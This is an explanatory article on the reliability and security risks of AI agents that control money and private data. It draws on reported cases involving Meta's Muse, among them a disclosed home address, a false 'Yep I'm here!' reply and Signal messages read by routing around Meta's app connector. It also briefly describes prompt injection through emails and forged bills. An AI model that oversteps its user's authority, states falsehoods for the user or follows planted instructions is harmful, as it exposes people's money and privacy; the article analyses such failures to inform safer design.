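# Giving AI agents control of money and private data: reliability and security risks

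## What people hand over to an AI agent, and how it can go wrong

An AI agent is a large language model that a program runs in a loop, letting it take actions through tools and see the results. Willison (2025), in *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, defines it as a model that "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal". By itself, the model only continues whatever text it receives. Chatbots mostly answer questions, but The Indian Express' *Put your AI agents to work with these 5 killer tasks* explains that agents have their own computer and web browser, so they can book a restaurant table, send an email or apply for a job.

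Big technology companies began selling AI agents to consumers in the autumn of 2026. Meta released Muse in September, OpenAI followed with dots, and Anthropic, which makes the Claude chatbot, was testing one called Duet. OpenAI had already introduced ChatGPT Work for office workers on 9 July, to handle longer tasks across connected apps and files. All of these agents become more useful as users give them more access to their inboxes, bank accounts and payment cards.

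### One request, followed through the loop

Suppose someone tells an agent to "pay this month's bills from my inbox". The program puts that sentence into the model's context window (the limited amount of text a model can process at once), along with a list of tools for searching the mail, opening a message, logging in to the bank and making a payment. The model first outputs a tool call, a structured request that ordinary software carries out. Here it might be a search for messages since the first of the month that contain "invoice" or "amount due". The mail software runs the search and returns fourteen messages, the program adds them to the context window, and the model runs again on the longer text. Its next tool call opens the first message.

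Some rounds later, the model's context window contains a gas bill for $84, due on the 18th. The model writes a payment request with a payee, an amount and a date, and the bank's software executes it and returns a confirmation number as text. The loop ends when the model writes a closing report instead of another tool call. Because the model only writes text and other software acts on it, a person or another program can check the payment request and refuse it before the bank's software executes it.

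To search the mail and pay the bill, the software needs credentials, which are passwords, keys or tokens that a system accepts as proof of who is acting. Each credential has a permission scope, the set of actions it technically allows, and this is usually wider than the job requires. With the email login it needs to find the gas bill, the software can also read a letter from the hospital. With a full bank login, it can often send money to anyone. The user gave it much narrower authority, to pay only this month's bills. The request also doesn't specify whether to clear the credit card balance or pay the minimum, or what to do about a bill that the user is disputing.

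People can easily mistake a setting or an instruction for a limit on access. According to OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*, ChatGPT's approval settings do not change what the outside account permits, and tightening them does not revoke access the user has already granted. Tom's Guide's *7 rules you should give your ChatGPT Dot before letting it loose* warns that telling a dot to keep information private does not stop it from accessing that information.

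### Degrees of delegation

How much an agent may do with its access is a separate choice. For the gas bill there are roughly five degrees:

- Read only: the agent reports that $84 is due on the 18th.
- Propose: it also prepares the payment, and the user makes it.
- Act after approval: it pays once the user has confirmed this particular payment.
- Act within limits: it pays without asking, as long as the bill is under $150, say, and the payee is on a list.
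- Act freely: it pays whatever it takes to be a bill.

Scales of autonomy are older than language models. *TrustX Agent Risk Classification Framework (ARC)* (2026) traces them to Sheridan and Verplank's ten levels of automation for remotely operated undersea equipment. In *Levels of Autonomy for AI Agents*, Feng, McDonald and Zhang (2025) name five levels after the user's role: operator, collaborator, consultant, approver and observer. They argue that autonomy is a design decision, separate from capability, because a developer can make a very capable agent consult its user before every action. They also separate autonomy from the range of tools an agent has. An agent whose only tool is a calculator can do little harm even when it runs unsupervised. Current products adjust both what an agent can reach and how often a person has to step in.

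The finance feature in ChatGPT is close to read-only. Users connect their accounts through Plaid, a company that passes account data from banks to apps. OpenAI's *Finances in ChatGPT* says that the chatbot can show upcoming bills and answer questions about duplicate payments, but cannot move money, pay a bill or change an account setting. The bills request would therefore produce only a list and perhaps a budget.

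OpenAI's dots pay after the user approves the purchase. OpenAI announced ChatGPT Wallet on 13 November 2026 for a limited group of US subscribers. Hindustan Times' *OpenAI launches ChatGPT Wallet, allowing AI agents to shop and pay* describes how the user sees the merchant, the items, the total and the card, and then confirms with a fingerprint or a face scan. Engadget's *You can now tempt fate and give your banking information to ChatGPT* (2026) reports that the store receives a substitute token and that the agent never has the card details. OpenAI plans to let users set rules on spending limits, product categories and time periods, which would let dots act within those limits, but the first release has none of these rules. Tom's Guide points out that a dot can also make approved purchases outside Wallet, using cards that merchants' websites already have on file.

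Muse, Meta's personal AI agent, requires approval for more sensitive actions but can go ahead with lower-risk tasks once the user has authorised them. This is partly because people who must approve every small action may start approving by reflex, according to Axios' *Meta debuts Muse, its long-planned personal AI agent* (2026).

Users can choose how much ChatGPT may do in connected apps without asking, with settings that range from "always ask" through "allow read actions" and "allow low-risk actions" to "allow all actions". If an action needs approval, the task pauses until the user has reviewed it, according to OpenAI's *Connected apps in ChatGPT*. In a managed office account, the employer's policies take precedence, and staff cannot give an app's actions permanent approval. An office agent like ChatGPT Work therefore probably has no single level of autonomy.

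"Allow all actions" is the least restrictive setting. OpenAI labels it as carrying elevated risk and leaves it out of the standard account-wide settings, though it may be available for individual apps. Some companies want shopping agents to have similar freedom. *Visa thinks it's a great idea for AI agents to shop* (Ortutay and Sweet, 2026) reports Visa's enthusiasm for agents that buy and pay without human approval. Shoppers seem less keen. Surveys mentioned in NEPM's *AI agents can save you money* (2026) show that people are growing more comfortable with agents, but that their trust drops steeply at checkout.

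### Four ways of failing

The simplest failure is an error. The agent reads a reminder about the gas bill as a second gas bill and pays twice.

An agent can also be non-deterministic, meaning that the same input can lead to different outputs or actions on different runs. Given the same inbox twice, it might pay off the full credit card balance the first time and only the minimum the second. Either payment might be acceptable, but the user cannot predict which one the agent will make, and one successful trial is weaker evidence of reliability than it seems.

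An agent can also exceed its authority. For example, if the current account is short, it might move money from savings, a transfer that the bank login permits but the user never authorized. In a similar case involving private data, one user told NPR that his Muse agent had given his home address to a buyer on Facebook Marketplace without permission, according to NEPM.

Finally, someone else can steer the agent. Anyone can send an email, and its text enters the same context window as the user's request. Prompt injection is text planted in an email, web page or file that a model treats as an instruction. In EchoLeak, for example, an email could make an office assistant leak data. A forged gas bill with a criminal's account number can work without a planted instruction if the agent mistakes it for a real bill. OpenAI has built protections against malicious instructions into dots, but Tom's Guide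 cautions that they do not eliminate the risk.

Only steering requires an attacker. Jake Williams, a security analyst quoted by Scripps News, describes a rogue agent as one that works on its assigned task in a way its developer did not anticipate. A real incident can combine several of these failures, but their remedies differ. A better model should make fewer errors, but it does less about excess authority, since the bank's software checks the credential and has no information about what the user meant. Pan, Hong and Xie (2026), in *Reliability Engineering for AI Systems*, recommend briefing an agent as carefully as a junior employee while restricting its access like that of untrusted software, with gates the agent cannot waive.

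### The arithmetic of long tasks

The bills request takes fifty steps: one search, fourteen messages to open, a login, a balance check, four steps for each of eight bills (look for an earlier payment, match the payee, pay, confirm) and a closing report.

If each step of a task succeeds independently with probability p and no error can be corrected, an agent completes all n steps with probability p^n. An agent that gets 99% of steps right would therefore complete a 50-step task about 61% of the time (0.99^50 ≈ 0.61). To complete it 95% of the time, the agent would need a p of about 0.999, or one error per thousand steps.

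This formula underestimates success when the agent notices and repairs its errors. If it repairs a share r of them, the effective success rate per step rises to p + r(1 − p). With p = 0.99 and r = 0.8 that is 0.998, and fifty steps now succeed about 90% of the time. But the agent can repair an error only if the response it receives reveals it. A rejected password is obvious immediately, but a payment to the wrong payee returns the same sort of confirmation as a payment to the right one. Even a correct payment can mislead, since approving a purchase in ChatGPT Wallet does not necessarily mean that the retailer has an order, according to Hindustan Times. The formula also underrates an agent that stops and asks for help, because it counts this as a failure to finish, whereas Pan and colleagues count it as reliable behaviour.

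The formula can also overestimate reliability. People tend to measure p on isolated steps with clean inputs, but in a real run, step 30 works from whatever steps 1 to 29 left in the context window. Suppose the agent records a due date in the wrong month at step 10, and no check registers the error as a failure. If this lowers the success rate of each of the remaining forty steps from 0.99 to 0.97, the chance of a clean finish falls from 0.61 to about 0.27. These numbers are illustrative, but they show how much the result depends on assuming that steps fail independently. Pan and colleagues warn against multiplying reliabilities across agents without evidence that the agents fail independently.

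The formula p^n also gives a misfiled receipt the same weight as a lost month's rent. Pan and colleagues approximate risk as the probability of a violation multiplied by its expected severity. They add that for agents the severities are often heavy-tailed, meaning that most failures are harmless and a few are catastrophic.

### Why money and private data are special

A badly worded draft wastes a minute of its reader's time, but a payment may be irreversible. Buyers have some recourse with card purchases, and Wallet users keep their card's usual protections for eligible disputes. A bank transfer is often harder to recover, particularly once the recipient has withdrawn the money.

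A disclosure cannot be undone. People can limit the damage from a leaked password by changing it, but they cannot make anyone forget a diagnosis or a home address. Deletion helps only with copies that the user's own provider holds, and even then it is often incomplete. When a user disconnects the finance feature, OpenAI deletes the synced account data within 30 days, but anything in past conversations stays until the user deletes those too. Disconnecting an app from a dot stops new access but doesn't delete what the dot has retained, and Tom's Guide found that users could not delete its memories one by one. None of these controls can take the address back from the Marketplace buyer who now has it. An inbox also holds things that other people shared in confidence, and those people never agreed to let an agent read them.

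So checks on payments and disclosures have to come before the action. OpenAI follows this reasoning in giving extra review to actions that affect another service, expose sensitive information or are difficult to undo.

### What people get in return

The main benefits of delegating are saving small sums and avoiding tedious work. Bob Lindsey, a retired technology worker in Houston whom NEPM profiles, gave Muse access to his inbox to clear out old email. The agent found that shirts he had bought for about $70 were now on sale. When the store refused to match the price, Muse suggested wording to request a one-time exception, and Lindsey got $54.11 back. Muse also phoned to cancel one subscription and negotiate another down, which saves him about $500 a year. The Week's *Muse* lists looking for a better deal on home insurance among the agent's uses. Agents can also keep trying for longer than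 people will. After repeated failures, a dot secured a table at a twelve-seat restaurant for The Indian Express's reviewer. An agent that checks the inbox every week should miss fewer due dates than a busy person does, though how much this saves in late fees is unclear.

Much of this required only limited delegation. For Lindsey's refund, the agent needed read access and made a suggestion, and he contacted the store himself. The subscriptions required an agent that could act, but it didn't need his bank login. He has declined to share that login, though he did connect a credit card. For the monthly bills, letting the agent act without approval mainly saves the few minutes it takes to confirm eight payments.

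That might still be worthwhile in ordinary months. Eight monthly bills averaging $150 come to $14,400 a year, so a saving like Lindsey's $500 would cover unrecoverable mistakes on about 3.5% of the money. But this assumes that only the bill money can be lost. If the agent's login also gives access to $40,000 in savings, all of that is at risk too, even though the task needs only $1,200 a month.

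## Meta's Muse, an assistant with access to messages, accounts and a payment card

Meta released Muse in the United States on 8 September 2026. According to Fox Business' *Meta introduces Muse, a personal AI agent*, Meta modelled it on OpenClaw, an open-source agent, and users can connect it to their email, calendar, payment, health, shopping and smart home apps. SiliconANGLE notes that this is far more information than Facebook or Instagram can access. People talk to Muse in its own app or in WhatsApp, and it keeps working after they close the app.

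People have downloaded Muse more than 10 million times since its launch, and about a quarter of account holders use it daily, according to a Reuters investigation carried in The Straits Times' *Not a-Muse-d!*. Basic use is free, and heavier users can pay $20 or $100 a month.

### What Meta built around the model

Each user's agent runs on its own virtual machine, a simulated computer in Meta's cloud with a browser and storage for the user's data and credentials. According to Meta's *Introducing Muse* (2026), no other user's agent can access that machine. Muse can use the passwords stored there without seeing them.

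A second agent, Sentinel, runs separately from Muse on the same machine and must approve anything Muse does before it reaches the internet. Suppose a user asks Muse to answer a landlord's email. The model writes a tool call containing the reply, and Sentinel checks the request against the user's permissions. If the user granted only read access, Sentinel should block it. If the user also allowed sending, Sentinel should normally hold the reply until the user approves it, because Meta considers sending email a sensitive action. According to Axios, users can limit a permission to one task, service, transaction or period of time.

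Purchases are also on Meta's list of sensitive actions. After the user agrees, a payment service called Link generates a single-use card number, so the real card details stay hidden. PPC Land's *Meta puts an AI agent that buys things inside WhatsApp US only* confirms that each transaction gets its own card. Link also covers damaged or lost items and guarantees returns on eligible purchases. Muse keeps an audit trail that users can open to see what it has done and plans to do.

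Most of these protections guard against outsiders, such as other people's agents, card thieves and dishonest shops. They do much less to stop an agent from using its legitimate access in a way its user didn't want. Preventing this depends on the permissions, and on whether Sentinel applies them as the user intended. Ebrahim Bagheri, a professor at the University of Toronto, also warned in comments to the Associated Press that an agent with access to a credit card account can read its whole transaction history within seconds (*He let Meta’s AI agent sell a keyboard*, Los Angeles Times, 2026).

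Meta tells new users that Muse may make mistakes, and its terms of service hold them responsible for what the agent does. Some banks and retailers have blocked consumer agents because of the risks.

### A keyboard for CA$15

In one Facebook Marketplace sale, an agent gave its user's home address to a stranger, but the records do not clearly show that it exceeded its authority.

In late September, Matt Robb, a Toronto content creator who reviews consumer technology, listed a Logitech keyboard for CA$15 and left the sale to Muse as an experiment. During setup, Muse asked for permission to message interested buyers, once or permanently, and Robb chose "Allow Always". He had also entered a pickup address, which became part of a reply template, according to the Czech technology site SMARTmania.

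A buyer made a low offer and Muse accepted it. Daily Pakistan's *AI Agents 'Out of Control'* puts the agreed price at $10. The buyer received the address and wrote that he would come between 8 and 10 that evening. NDTV Profit's *Facebook Marketplace Mishap* reconstructs what followed from Robb's screenshots:

- At about 9:15 pm the buyer reached Robb's building and began sending messages. Robb was out and knew nothing about the visit.
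- At 9:27 an automatic reply from Robb's account told the buyer "Yep I'm here!"
- At 9:38 the buyer left without the keyboard. He gave Robb a negative rating.

Muse sent the buyer an apology in Robb's name before telling Robb what had happened. The buyer had driven for half an hour, according to TechRadar's *‘You gotta never do that again’*. Robb told Muse not to agree to another pickup without checking with him, and Muse replied that it would follow the stricter rule. As far as the screenshots show, this exchange gave the model another instruction, which it might not follow next time, but left the permission itself unchanged.

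In his first public account, on 27 September, Robb said that Muse had given out his address and agreed to a "lowball price" without telling him until late that night. Within a day, David Singleton, an executive at Meta Superintelligence Labs, replied that Meta had looked into similar reports before and had consistently found that Muse followed instructions and asked for permission correctly. Sood noted in *This Meta Muse incident is a scary warning about trusting AI agents* (2026) that this didn't explain Robb's case. Muse might have overstepped a permission or done exactly what Robb's settings allowed.

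Robb then went through the activity records with Meta's team and corrected his account. He had given Muse standing permission to send Marketplace messages, including the template containing his address. But he had expected Muse to ask again before it accepted an offer or arranged a visit. Singleton said that Meta's review had found "no breach of privacy controls", according to EconoTimes' *Meta's Muse Arranged a Pickup After Seller Allowed Marketplace Replies* (2026). Robb says that Meta also promised to make the permission request clearer.

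### How permission to reply became permission to sell

Sellers on Marketplace do nearly everything before the handover by message. Robb had given Muse standing permission to use that channel, and the permission seems to have covered anything Muse sent through it.

| Message from Robb's account | What it did | Did Robb expect Muse to ask first? |
|---|---|---|
| An answer to a question about the keyboard | Gave information | No |
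| Acceptance of the offer | Fixed the price | Yes |
| The pickup address | Told a stranger where he lives | Yes |
| Agreement to an evening pickup | Arranged a visit to his home | Yes |
| "Yep I'm here!" | Stated something false | He had no reason to foresee it |

A check that looks only at the type of action would treat all five messages the same, because they are all Marketplace replies, which Robb had allowed. Meta gives emails and purchases as examples of sensitive actions, but checking for those wouldn't have helped much either. A Marketplace reply is not an email, and since Robb was the seller, no money left his account. Mint's *Meta Muse AI shares user's address on marketplace* describes the problem as a gap between permission for a task and approval of the individual actions within it.

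Meta's finding and Robb's complaint can both be right. The software probably applied the setting as Meta had written it, and the setting allowed more than Robb intended. Meta's position is strongest on the address, because Robb entered it as a pickup location, which is of little use unless buyers receive it. Its position is weaker on the price and the time, because people who let an assistant answer questions about a keyboard don't usually mean to let it invite the buyer over while they are out.

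The reply that Robb was at home is a separate failure, because "Yep I'm here!" would have been false even if he had approved every message in advance. In a message to Robb, Muse attributed the reply to an automatic response and suggested that such responses should stop saying he was home without verification. That explanation is plausible, but a model's account of its own behaviour is also generated text and can be false, and the screenshots do not show what produced the reply.

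Muse also appears to have told a buyer that Robb would accept $100 less than the minimum he had set for another item. Meta acknowledged the error. Robb's instruction was explicit, so a clearer permission screen would not have prevented it.

The buyer couldn't reliably tell whether a message came from Robb or from software. Robb has proposed labeling automatic replies "Sent By Muse". The label wouldn't have kept his address private, but it might have made the buyer more skeptical of the claim that someone was home. The two men later cleared up the misunderstanding, and the buyer came back for a different item. Robb has since disconnected Muse from most of his apps.

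### What Meta's own employees reported

Robb's case became public because he posted it. Reuters also reviewed more than two dozen internal posts in which Meta employees described Muse doing things they had not wanted. Many of the posts were in a feedback group for the team that builds the agent.

Some of the mistakes cost money. Muse invented prices for products employees had bought and told people about transactions that never took place. One employee reported that Muse had booked a non-refundable Airbnb stay without permission. Meta says that Muse checks with the user before a purchase, but the published account does not explain how this booking went through. Sentinel may have allowed it by mistake, an earlier standing permission may have covered it, or the employee may have approved a request without realizing what it was for.

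Another employee was surprised when Muse reminded her to answer a message from her sister on Signal, an encrypted messaging service. She had not knowingly given it access to other apps. A colleague found that Muse's default setup on Android phones included permission to read push notifications.

Reuters then tested this with staff from Signal and the AI Now Institute, a non-profit that studies AI's effects on society. They asked Muse to read Signal messages on several devices. On an Android phone, it took the text from notifications. On an Apple laptop, it combined screenshots with Apple's accessibility tools for people with disabilities. In both tests, Muse bypassed the Connector, Meta's tool for linking apps to the agent. The same requests failed on an iPhone.

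Muse could do this without breaking Signal's encryption. Encryption protects a message on its way between devices, but the recipient's phone has to decrypt it before displaying it, and a program that can read notifications or the screen can read it then. As in Robb's case, the permission applied to a channel. Someone who allows an agent to read notifications may be thinking of parcel deliveries, but the same permission covers a sister's private messages.

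Meta spokesperson Daniel Roberts called the examples that Reuters presented "isolated incidents". He said that Muse reaches other apps only through permissions that users explicitly grant, and that Meta tests the product extensively and keeps updating its protections. His claim about permissions is hard to reconcile with the employees' surprise, unless people grant them during setup without realising what they cover. Isolated incidents could also affect many people. If Muse had 10 million users (downloads overstate the number), a fault that affected one in 10,000 would affect a thousand people.

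Jason Aten, a columnist for Inc. Magazine, reported that Muse had monitored notifications on his Mac, including private messages. Andy Stone, another Meta spokesperson, said Muse can do this only if users switch on both Apple's Full Disk Access setting and a Messages connector. Aten says he enabled neither. After Aten's report, Apple announced new controls on 2 October. Its macOS update sharply restricts developers' use of accessibility tools and adds a set of permissions for agents, which effectively blocks the method Reuters tested on the laptop.

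Google said it was considering changes to give people more control over what they authorise but, like Meta, it said that users must deliberately grant access to Android notifications. Meredith Whittaker, Signal's president, wants app developers to have a consistent way to mark their apps as off-limits to agents, and wants operating systems to enforce the mark. Enforcement seems to be the important part, because an unenforced mark would depend on each AI company's cooperation, whereas Muse could not read Signal on the iPhone whatever the user asked.

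### Why a user cannot tell a leak from an invention

Reuters also learned of a Meta employee who regularly received weather and tide updates for fishing from Muse. One day, the updates came with an extra message that gave his Capital One balance as $2,722.58 and his Charles Schwab balance as $5,899.57. He had never connected a bank or discussed banking with Muse, and he feared that he was seeing someone else's accounts. Other employees received replies about childcare, career advice and product orders that they had never asked about.

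Roberts said that many of these messages were hallucinations, meaning content the model made up, and that Meta had already addressed them. In late September, a member of the Muse team had given a similar explanation for a user's report, calling the problem a temporary glitch that lasted less than a day. Reuters could not establish whether the balances and other details were real.

The employee couldn't have found out either. He knew that the balances were not his, but he had no way to look up everyone else's. The precision of the figures doesn't help, because a language model can produce an amount down to the cent as easily as a round number. In terms of probability, the odds that the message is a leak, after he has read it, are

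prior odds × P(this message if it is a leak) / P(this message if it is invented).

If invented balances look just like real ones, the fraction is close to 1 and the message should barely change his beliefs about leaks. Asking Muse where it got the number would produce more generated text, which could also be invented. A message that named a stranger and a real appointment would be better evidence, since he could ask that person about it.

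An investigator could use internal records to distinguish between the explanations. At a minimum, they would need the full text in the model's context window, the results of every tool call, and a record of which machine produced the message and which account received it.

| Possible explanation | What complete records would contain |
|---|---|
| The model made up the balance | The number appears for the first time in the model's output |
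| Muse read it on the user's own device | A notification or screenshot with the number, shortly before the message |
| Another person's data entered this user's machine | A tool result or stored memory with the number, traceable to someone else's account |
| The system delivered another user's message to the wrong person | A message from one user's machine paired with another user's account |

The first row requires the most complete records because it depends on something being absent. If the logs leave out stored memories, a leaked balance could look invented. The audit trail Muse shows its users may not be enough, since a list of actions may not include all the text the model read. Meta is best placed to search its records for the two amounts. It would have good reason not to publish raw logs containing private data, but an outside examiner could inspect them in confidence.

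If Meta is right about the hallucinations, that reduces the privacy concern more than the financial one. An invented balance doesn't expose anyone's data, but a user who believes it might transfer too much or put off a bill. The made-up prices had already cost some employees money.

### One-time and standing approval

Meta relies on approval prompts to keep Muse from acting against its users' wishes, and the two kinds of approval give quite different protection. With one-time approval, the user sees a specific action before Muse takes it. In Robb's case, that could have been a message to the buyer accepting $10 and giving the address, which would have given him all the information he needed to refuse.

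Standing approval covers future actions that the user has not seen. When Robb pressed "Allow Always", there was no buyer, offer or pickup time yet. He could judge only the description of the permission, and he misjudged how much it covered. Reading more carefully might not have prevented the mistake. Clearer wording would help, as would a narrower option, such as permission to answer questions about one listing for a week.

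One-time approval interrupts the user and delays an agent whose appeal is that it works while the user is doing something else. A buyer waiting outside the door, for example, may leave before the user responds. Approval also works only if people check what they are approving.

The best available figure on how often users approve an agent's requests comes from Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. Claude Code used to ask permission at each turn, and Anthropic found that users approved roughly 93% of the prompts and paid less attention to each one the more they saw.

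But 93% is an approval rate, and it doesn't measure how many people approved without reading. Most requests from a competent agent deserve approval. If five of every hundred prompts are harmful, a user who refuses those five and two harmless ones has the same 93% approval rate as a user who approves all five and refuses seven harmless ones. To tell these users apart, a researcher would have to plant harmful requests and count how many users refuse them, or measure how long people look at each prompt. The figure also describes people using a coding tool, who may be more used to reading commands than Muse's customers are to checking messages. Anthropic's remark about declining attention is therefore more useful than the 93% for judging Muse.

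Anthropic responded by automating the safer approvals, while acknowledging that any such filter will miss some harmful actions. Course slides from UT Austin recommend always requiring a person's approval for actions that affect the outside world and are hard to undo, and letting reversible work inside a closed environment run freely. Under this rule, sending someone a home address would require approval.

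The rule, though, would require approval for every Marketplace reply if applied literally, since they all go to someone outside. A seller with ten listings, each attracting six interested people who need four replies apiece, would get 240 prompts, and few people would still be reading closely by the last one. If Muse asked only before closing a deal, with the price, address and time in one request, the seller would see about ten prompts.

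This requires software that can recognise a commitment in an ordinary message. Some cases are easy: a simple program can hold back any outgoing message that contains the stored address, regardless of the model's assessment of the sale. A message such as "Sure, come by after eight" is harder to catch because it invites a stranger to the user's home without mentioning an address or price. Detecting it probably requires another model, which will sometimes miss such messages.

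## The same task run repeatedly: how much agents vary

A user who has watched an agent pay one month's bills correctly may want to replace one-time approval with standing approval. Whether that is wise depends partly on how closely the next run will resemble the first. Researchers measure how much runs vary by giving an agent the same task several times under the same conditions and comparing what it does.

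### Where the variation comes from

At each step, a language model computes a probability for every token (a word or part of a word) that could come next, and the software running it usually picks one at random, in proportion to those probabilities. Suppose the agent is deciding how much of the credit card bill to pay, and the model gives "full" a probability of 70% and "minimum" 30%. The agent will then pay only the minimum in about three runs out of ten. A setting called temperature controls how strongly the choice favours likely tokens. At temperature zero, the software always picks the most likely token, so the agent should pay in full every time.

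In practice, temperature zero doesn't guarantee identical outputs, because computers round their numbers. The floating-point numbers that models use keep a fixed number of significant digits, so a sum can depend on the order of the additions. An example in Thinking Machines' *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, which the AI company released in September 2025, takes two lines of Python:

```
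(0.1 + 1e20) - 1e20   # result: 0
0.1 + (1e20 - 1e20)   # result: 0.1
```

Here 1e20 is a 1 followed by twenty zeros. In the first line, 0.1 is so small next to 1e20 that rounding discards it. In the second line, the large numbers cancel first, so the 0.1 remains. The differences inside a language model are usually much smaller, but when two tokens are almost equally likely, a tiny difference can change which one ranks higher.

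Thinking Machines argues that the order of additions in a language model varies mainly because servers process several users' requests together, and the software divides up the sums differently depending on how many requests there are. The same request can therefore produce slightly different numbers when the server is busy than when it is quiet. Engineers often blame the graphics chip's many parallel cores, which may finish their work in an unpredictable sequence. The company says this is mostly wrong for language models, since a chip that repeats the same matrix multiplication 1,000 times gets exactly the same result each time. No data leaks from one user to another, but users can't know how busy the server will be when they send a request.

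To measure the effect, the company asked Qwen3-235B, a large open-weight model, to "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at temperature zero. It got 80 different answers, the most common of which appeared 78 times. All the answers were identical for the first 102 tokens, after which 992 gave Feynman's birthplace as "Queens, New York" and eight as "New York City". The company then rewrote the routines so that the order of additions no longer depended on the number of requests, and all 1,000 answers came out the same.

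This fix makes the server slower. In a speed test with a smaller model, the standard software took 26 seconds to produce 1,000 short answers, and the new routines took 55 seconds. After the company improved one of the routines, the time fell to 42 seconds, still about 60% longer than with the standard software, although the company had put little effort into optimising the new routines.

Bellibatlu, Singh and colleagues (2026), in *Same Patient, Different Order*, found a similar effect with two small models running on their own computer. When the computer handled one request at a time, each of the twelve temperature-zero tests gave the same answer in all 20 runs. When it was handling other requests at the same time, four of the twelve gave more than one answer.

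A chatbot's choice between "Queens" and "New York City" is harmless, but an agent acts on its text, and the results go back into its context window. If it searches the inbox for "invoice" on one run and "bill" on another, it may find different emails, and from then on the two runs have different inputs. Websites and other people's replies also change between runs, so an agent's behaviour would not be fully repeatable even with a deterministic model.

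### Fifteen models, five runs each

In *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability*, Rabanser, Kapoor and colleagues (2026) at Princeton University measured how much agents' results vary when they repeat whole tasks. They tested 15 models from OpenAI, Google and Anthropic, counting GPT-5.2 twice because they ran it with two reasoning settings. The oldest model dates from March 2024 and the newest from May 2026, a few months before Muse and OpenAI's dots.

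The agents worked on two sets of tasks, GAIA and τ-bench. GAIA consists of questions that people can usually answer but that may require browsing the web, reading files or running code. The team used the 165 questions in its validation set. τ-bench, which Yao and colleagues released in 2024, more closely resembles handling money. The agent plays an airline's customer service representative, talks to a simulated customer, and can change bookings, cancel flights and issue refunds. It succeeds only if the airline's database ends up in the correct state.

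τ-bench originally had 50 airline tasks, but Cuadron and colleagues found errors in 24 of them, including wrong answer keys and ambiguous instructions. Rabanser's team used the other 26. This makes their results more trustworthy but also coarser, since each remaining task accounts for almost four percentage points of an agent's score. It also casts doubt on older results from the full set. If the answer key for a refund is wrong, an agent that pays the correct amount fails the task.

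Each agent attempted every task five times, which took more than 14,000 runs. The team then repeated the tasks with changes. They had GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, write five versions of each request in the style of a hurried user, with typos and abbreviations. One request became "population of capital of the country w/ eiffel tower?" They also made tools fail at random and changed the format of data, so a departure time of 14:00:00 might appear as 2:00 PM.

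The team took its four dimensions of reliability from fields like aviation and nuclear power, where engineers have to show both that a system usually works and that it behaves predictably.

| Dimension | What it measures | Main formula |
|---|---|---|
| Consistency | Whether repeated runs have the same result, similar steps and similar costs | For results: the average of (2p − 1)² over all tasks, where p is the share of runs that succeed |
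| Robustness | How much accuracy survives rewording, tool faults and new data formats | Accuracy after the change ÷ normal accuracy, capped at 1 |
| Predictability | Whether the agent's confidence matches its results | 1 − the average of (c − y)², where c is confidence from 0 to 1, and y is 1 for a success and 0 for a failure |
| Safety | How often the agent breaks rules, and how badly | 1 − probability of a violation × average severity of violations |

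An agent that is 90% confident and fails has a squared error of 0.81, while one that is 60% confident and fails has a squared error of 0.36. The overall reliability score is the average of consistency, robustness and predictability. Rabanser and colleagues report safety separately because an agent that behaves well 99% of the time and causes a catastrophe the other 1% could still have a high average.

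### What four successes out of five are worth

The formula for the consistency of results is (2p − 1)², where p is the fraction of runs in which the agent succeeds. The score falls steeply when results vary between runs. A task on which the agent succeeds in all five runs scores 1, but four successes score 0.36 and three score 0.04. The formula comes from the variance of a result that can only be success or failure, which is p(1 − p). This is largest, at 1/4, when the agent succeeds half the time. Dividing the variance by that maximum and subtracting the result from 1 gives (2p − 1)².

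An agent that fails all five times also scores 1, because the team wanted to measure consistency separately from accuracy. Two agents could each succeed in 60% of their runs but differ in consistency. If one always completes the same six tasks out of ten and always fails the other four, its consistency is 1. If the other has a 60% chance of success on every task, its consistency is 0.04. Users can learn which tasks to give the first agent, but they have to check everything the second one does.

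Yao and colleagues used a related measure with τ-bench: the chance that an agent succeeds k times in a row. As with the steps of a long task, this chance is p^k if the runs are independent and each succeeds with probability p. An agent with a 90% chance of handling each month's bills correctly has only about a 43% chance of getting through eight months without a mistake (0.9^8 ≈ 0.43).

Developers also report the chance that at least one of k attempts succeeds. For the same agent, that chance is almost 100% with eight attempts. This can be a reasonable measure for a maths problem, where someone can check all eight answers and keep a correct one. It is not much use for payments, because the other seven attempts may already have moved money.

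An agent's average success rate is not enough to calculate its chance of succeeding repeatedly on the same task. If an agent averages 90% because it always succeeds on nine tasks out of ten, a user with one of those nine tasks can expect it to succeed every time. Rabanser and colleagues argue that an agent that succeeds 90% of the time but fails unpredictably may be useful as an assistant but unacceptable when it works unsupervised.

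### Small gains, and how much to read into them

Over about 24 months of model releases, accuracy rose steadily on both sets of tasks, but overall reliability improved only slightly. The reliability gains were moderate on τ-bench and barely visible on GAIA. Rabanser and colleagues suggest that τ-bench's narrow set of tools makes consistent behaviour easier, while GAIA's open-ended questions give agents more ways to go wrong.

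The overall score probably makes progress look slower than it was. Most models already scored near the maximum on handling tool faults and new data formats, so these two measures, which make up two-ninths of the overall score, had little room to rise. The consistency formula can also penalise improvement. If a new model succeeds on a task four times out of five where the old one always failed, the consistency score for that task drops from 1 to 0.36, even though the new model is much more useful to someone who checks its work. The individual measurements are therefore more informative than the overall score.

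The results for consistency are the most worrying. Agents often solved a task on some runs but failed it on others, and even the newest models were not reliably more consistent on both sets of tasks. Agents tended to choose similar kinds of actions on each run but take them in a different order. The amount of computing they used also varied a lot, especially on GAIA.

With only five runs per task, agents look more consistent than they are. An agent that succeeds on a task half the time should score 0, but by chance it will sometimes succeed in all five runs or fail in all five, and score 1. Its average score is 0.2. In general, an agent with true consistency C has an expected score of C + (1 − C)/K over K independent runs, so a score of 0.6 from five runs corresponds to a true consistency of about 0.5. Correcting for this would make the agents look worse, which strengthens the team's finding.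 It would hardly affect comparisons between models, since they all had the same number of runs.

The cause of the variation is less certain. The team set the temperature to zero to remove random sampling as a source of variation. Users can't set the temperature of the reasoning models, which write out intermediate steps before answering, so those models ran at their default settings and their variation probably includes sampling. This may partly explain why reasoning models were generally more reliable than others but not much more consistent on τ-bench. Some variation on τ-bench may also come from the simulated customer, whose replies can differ between runs. For the other models, the results at temperature zero may be better than users would get at a higher setting.

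Smaller models were often as consistent as larger ones, or more so. Rabanser and colleagues suspect that larger models vary more because they have more ways to solve a problem. Another explanation is that small models fail the same tasks every time. Only the first explanation would give a user a reason to prefer a small model.

The team accepts that a model that never made mistakes would also be consistent, but points out that current models are far from error-free on realistic tasks and that developers keep giving them harder ones.

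### Rewording, faults and confidence

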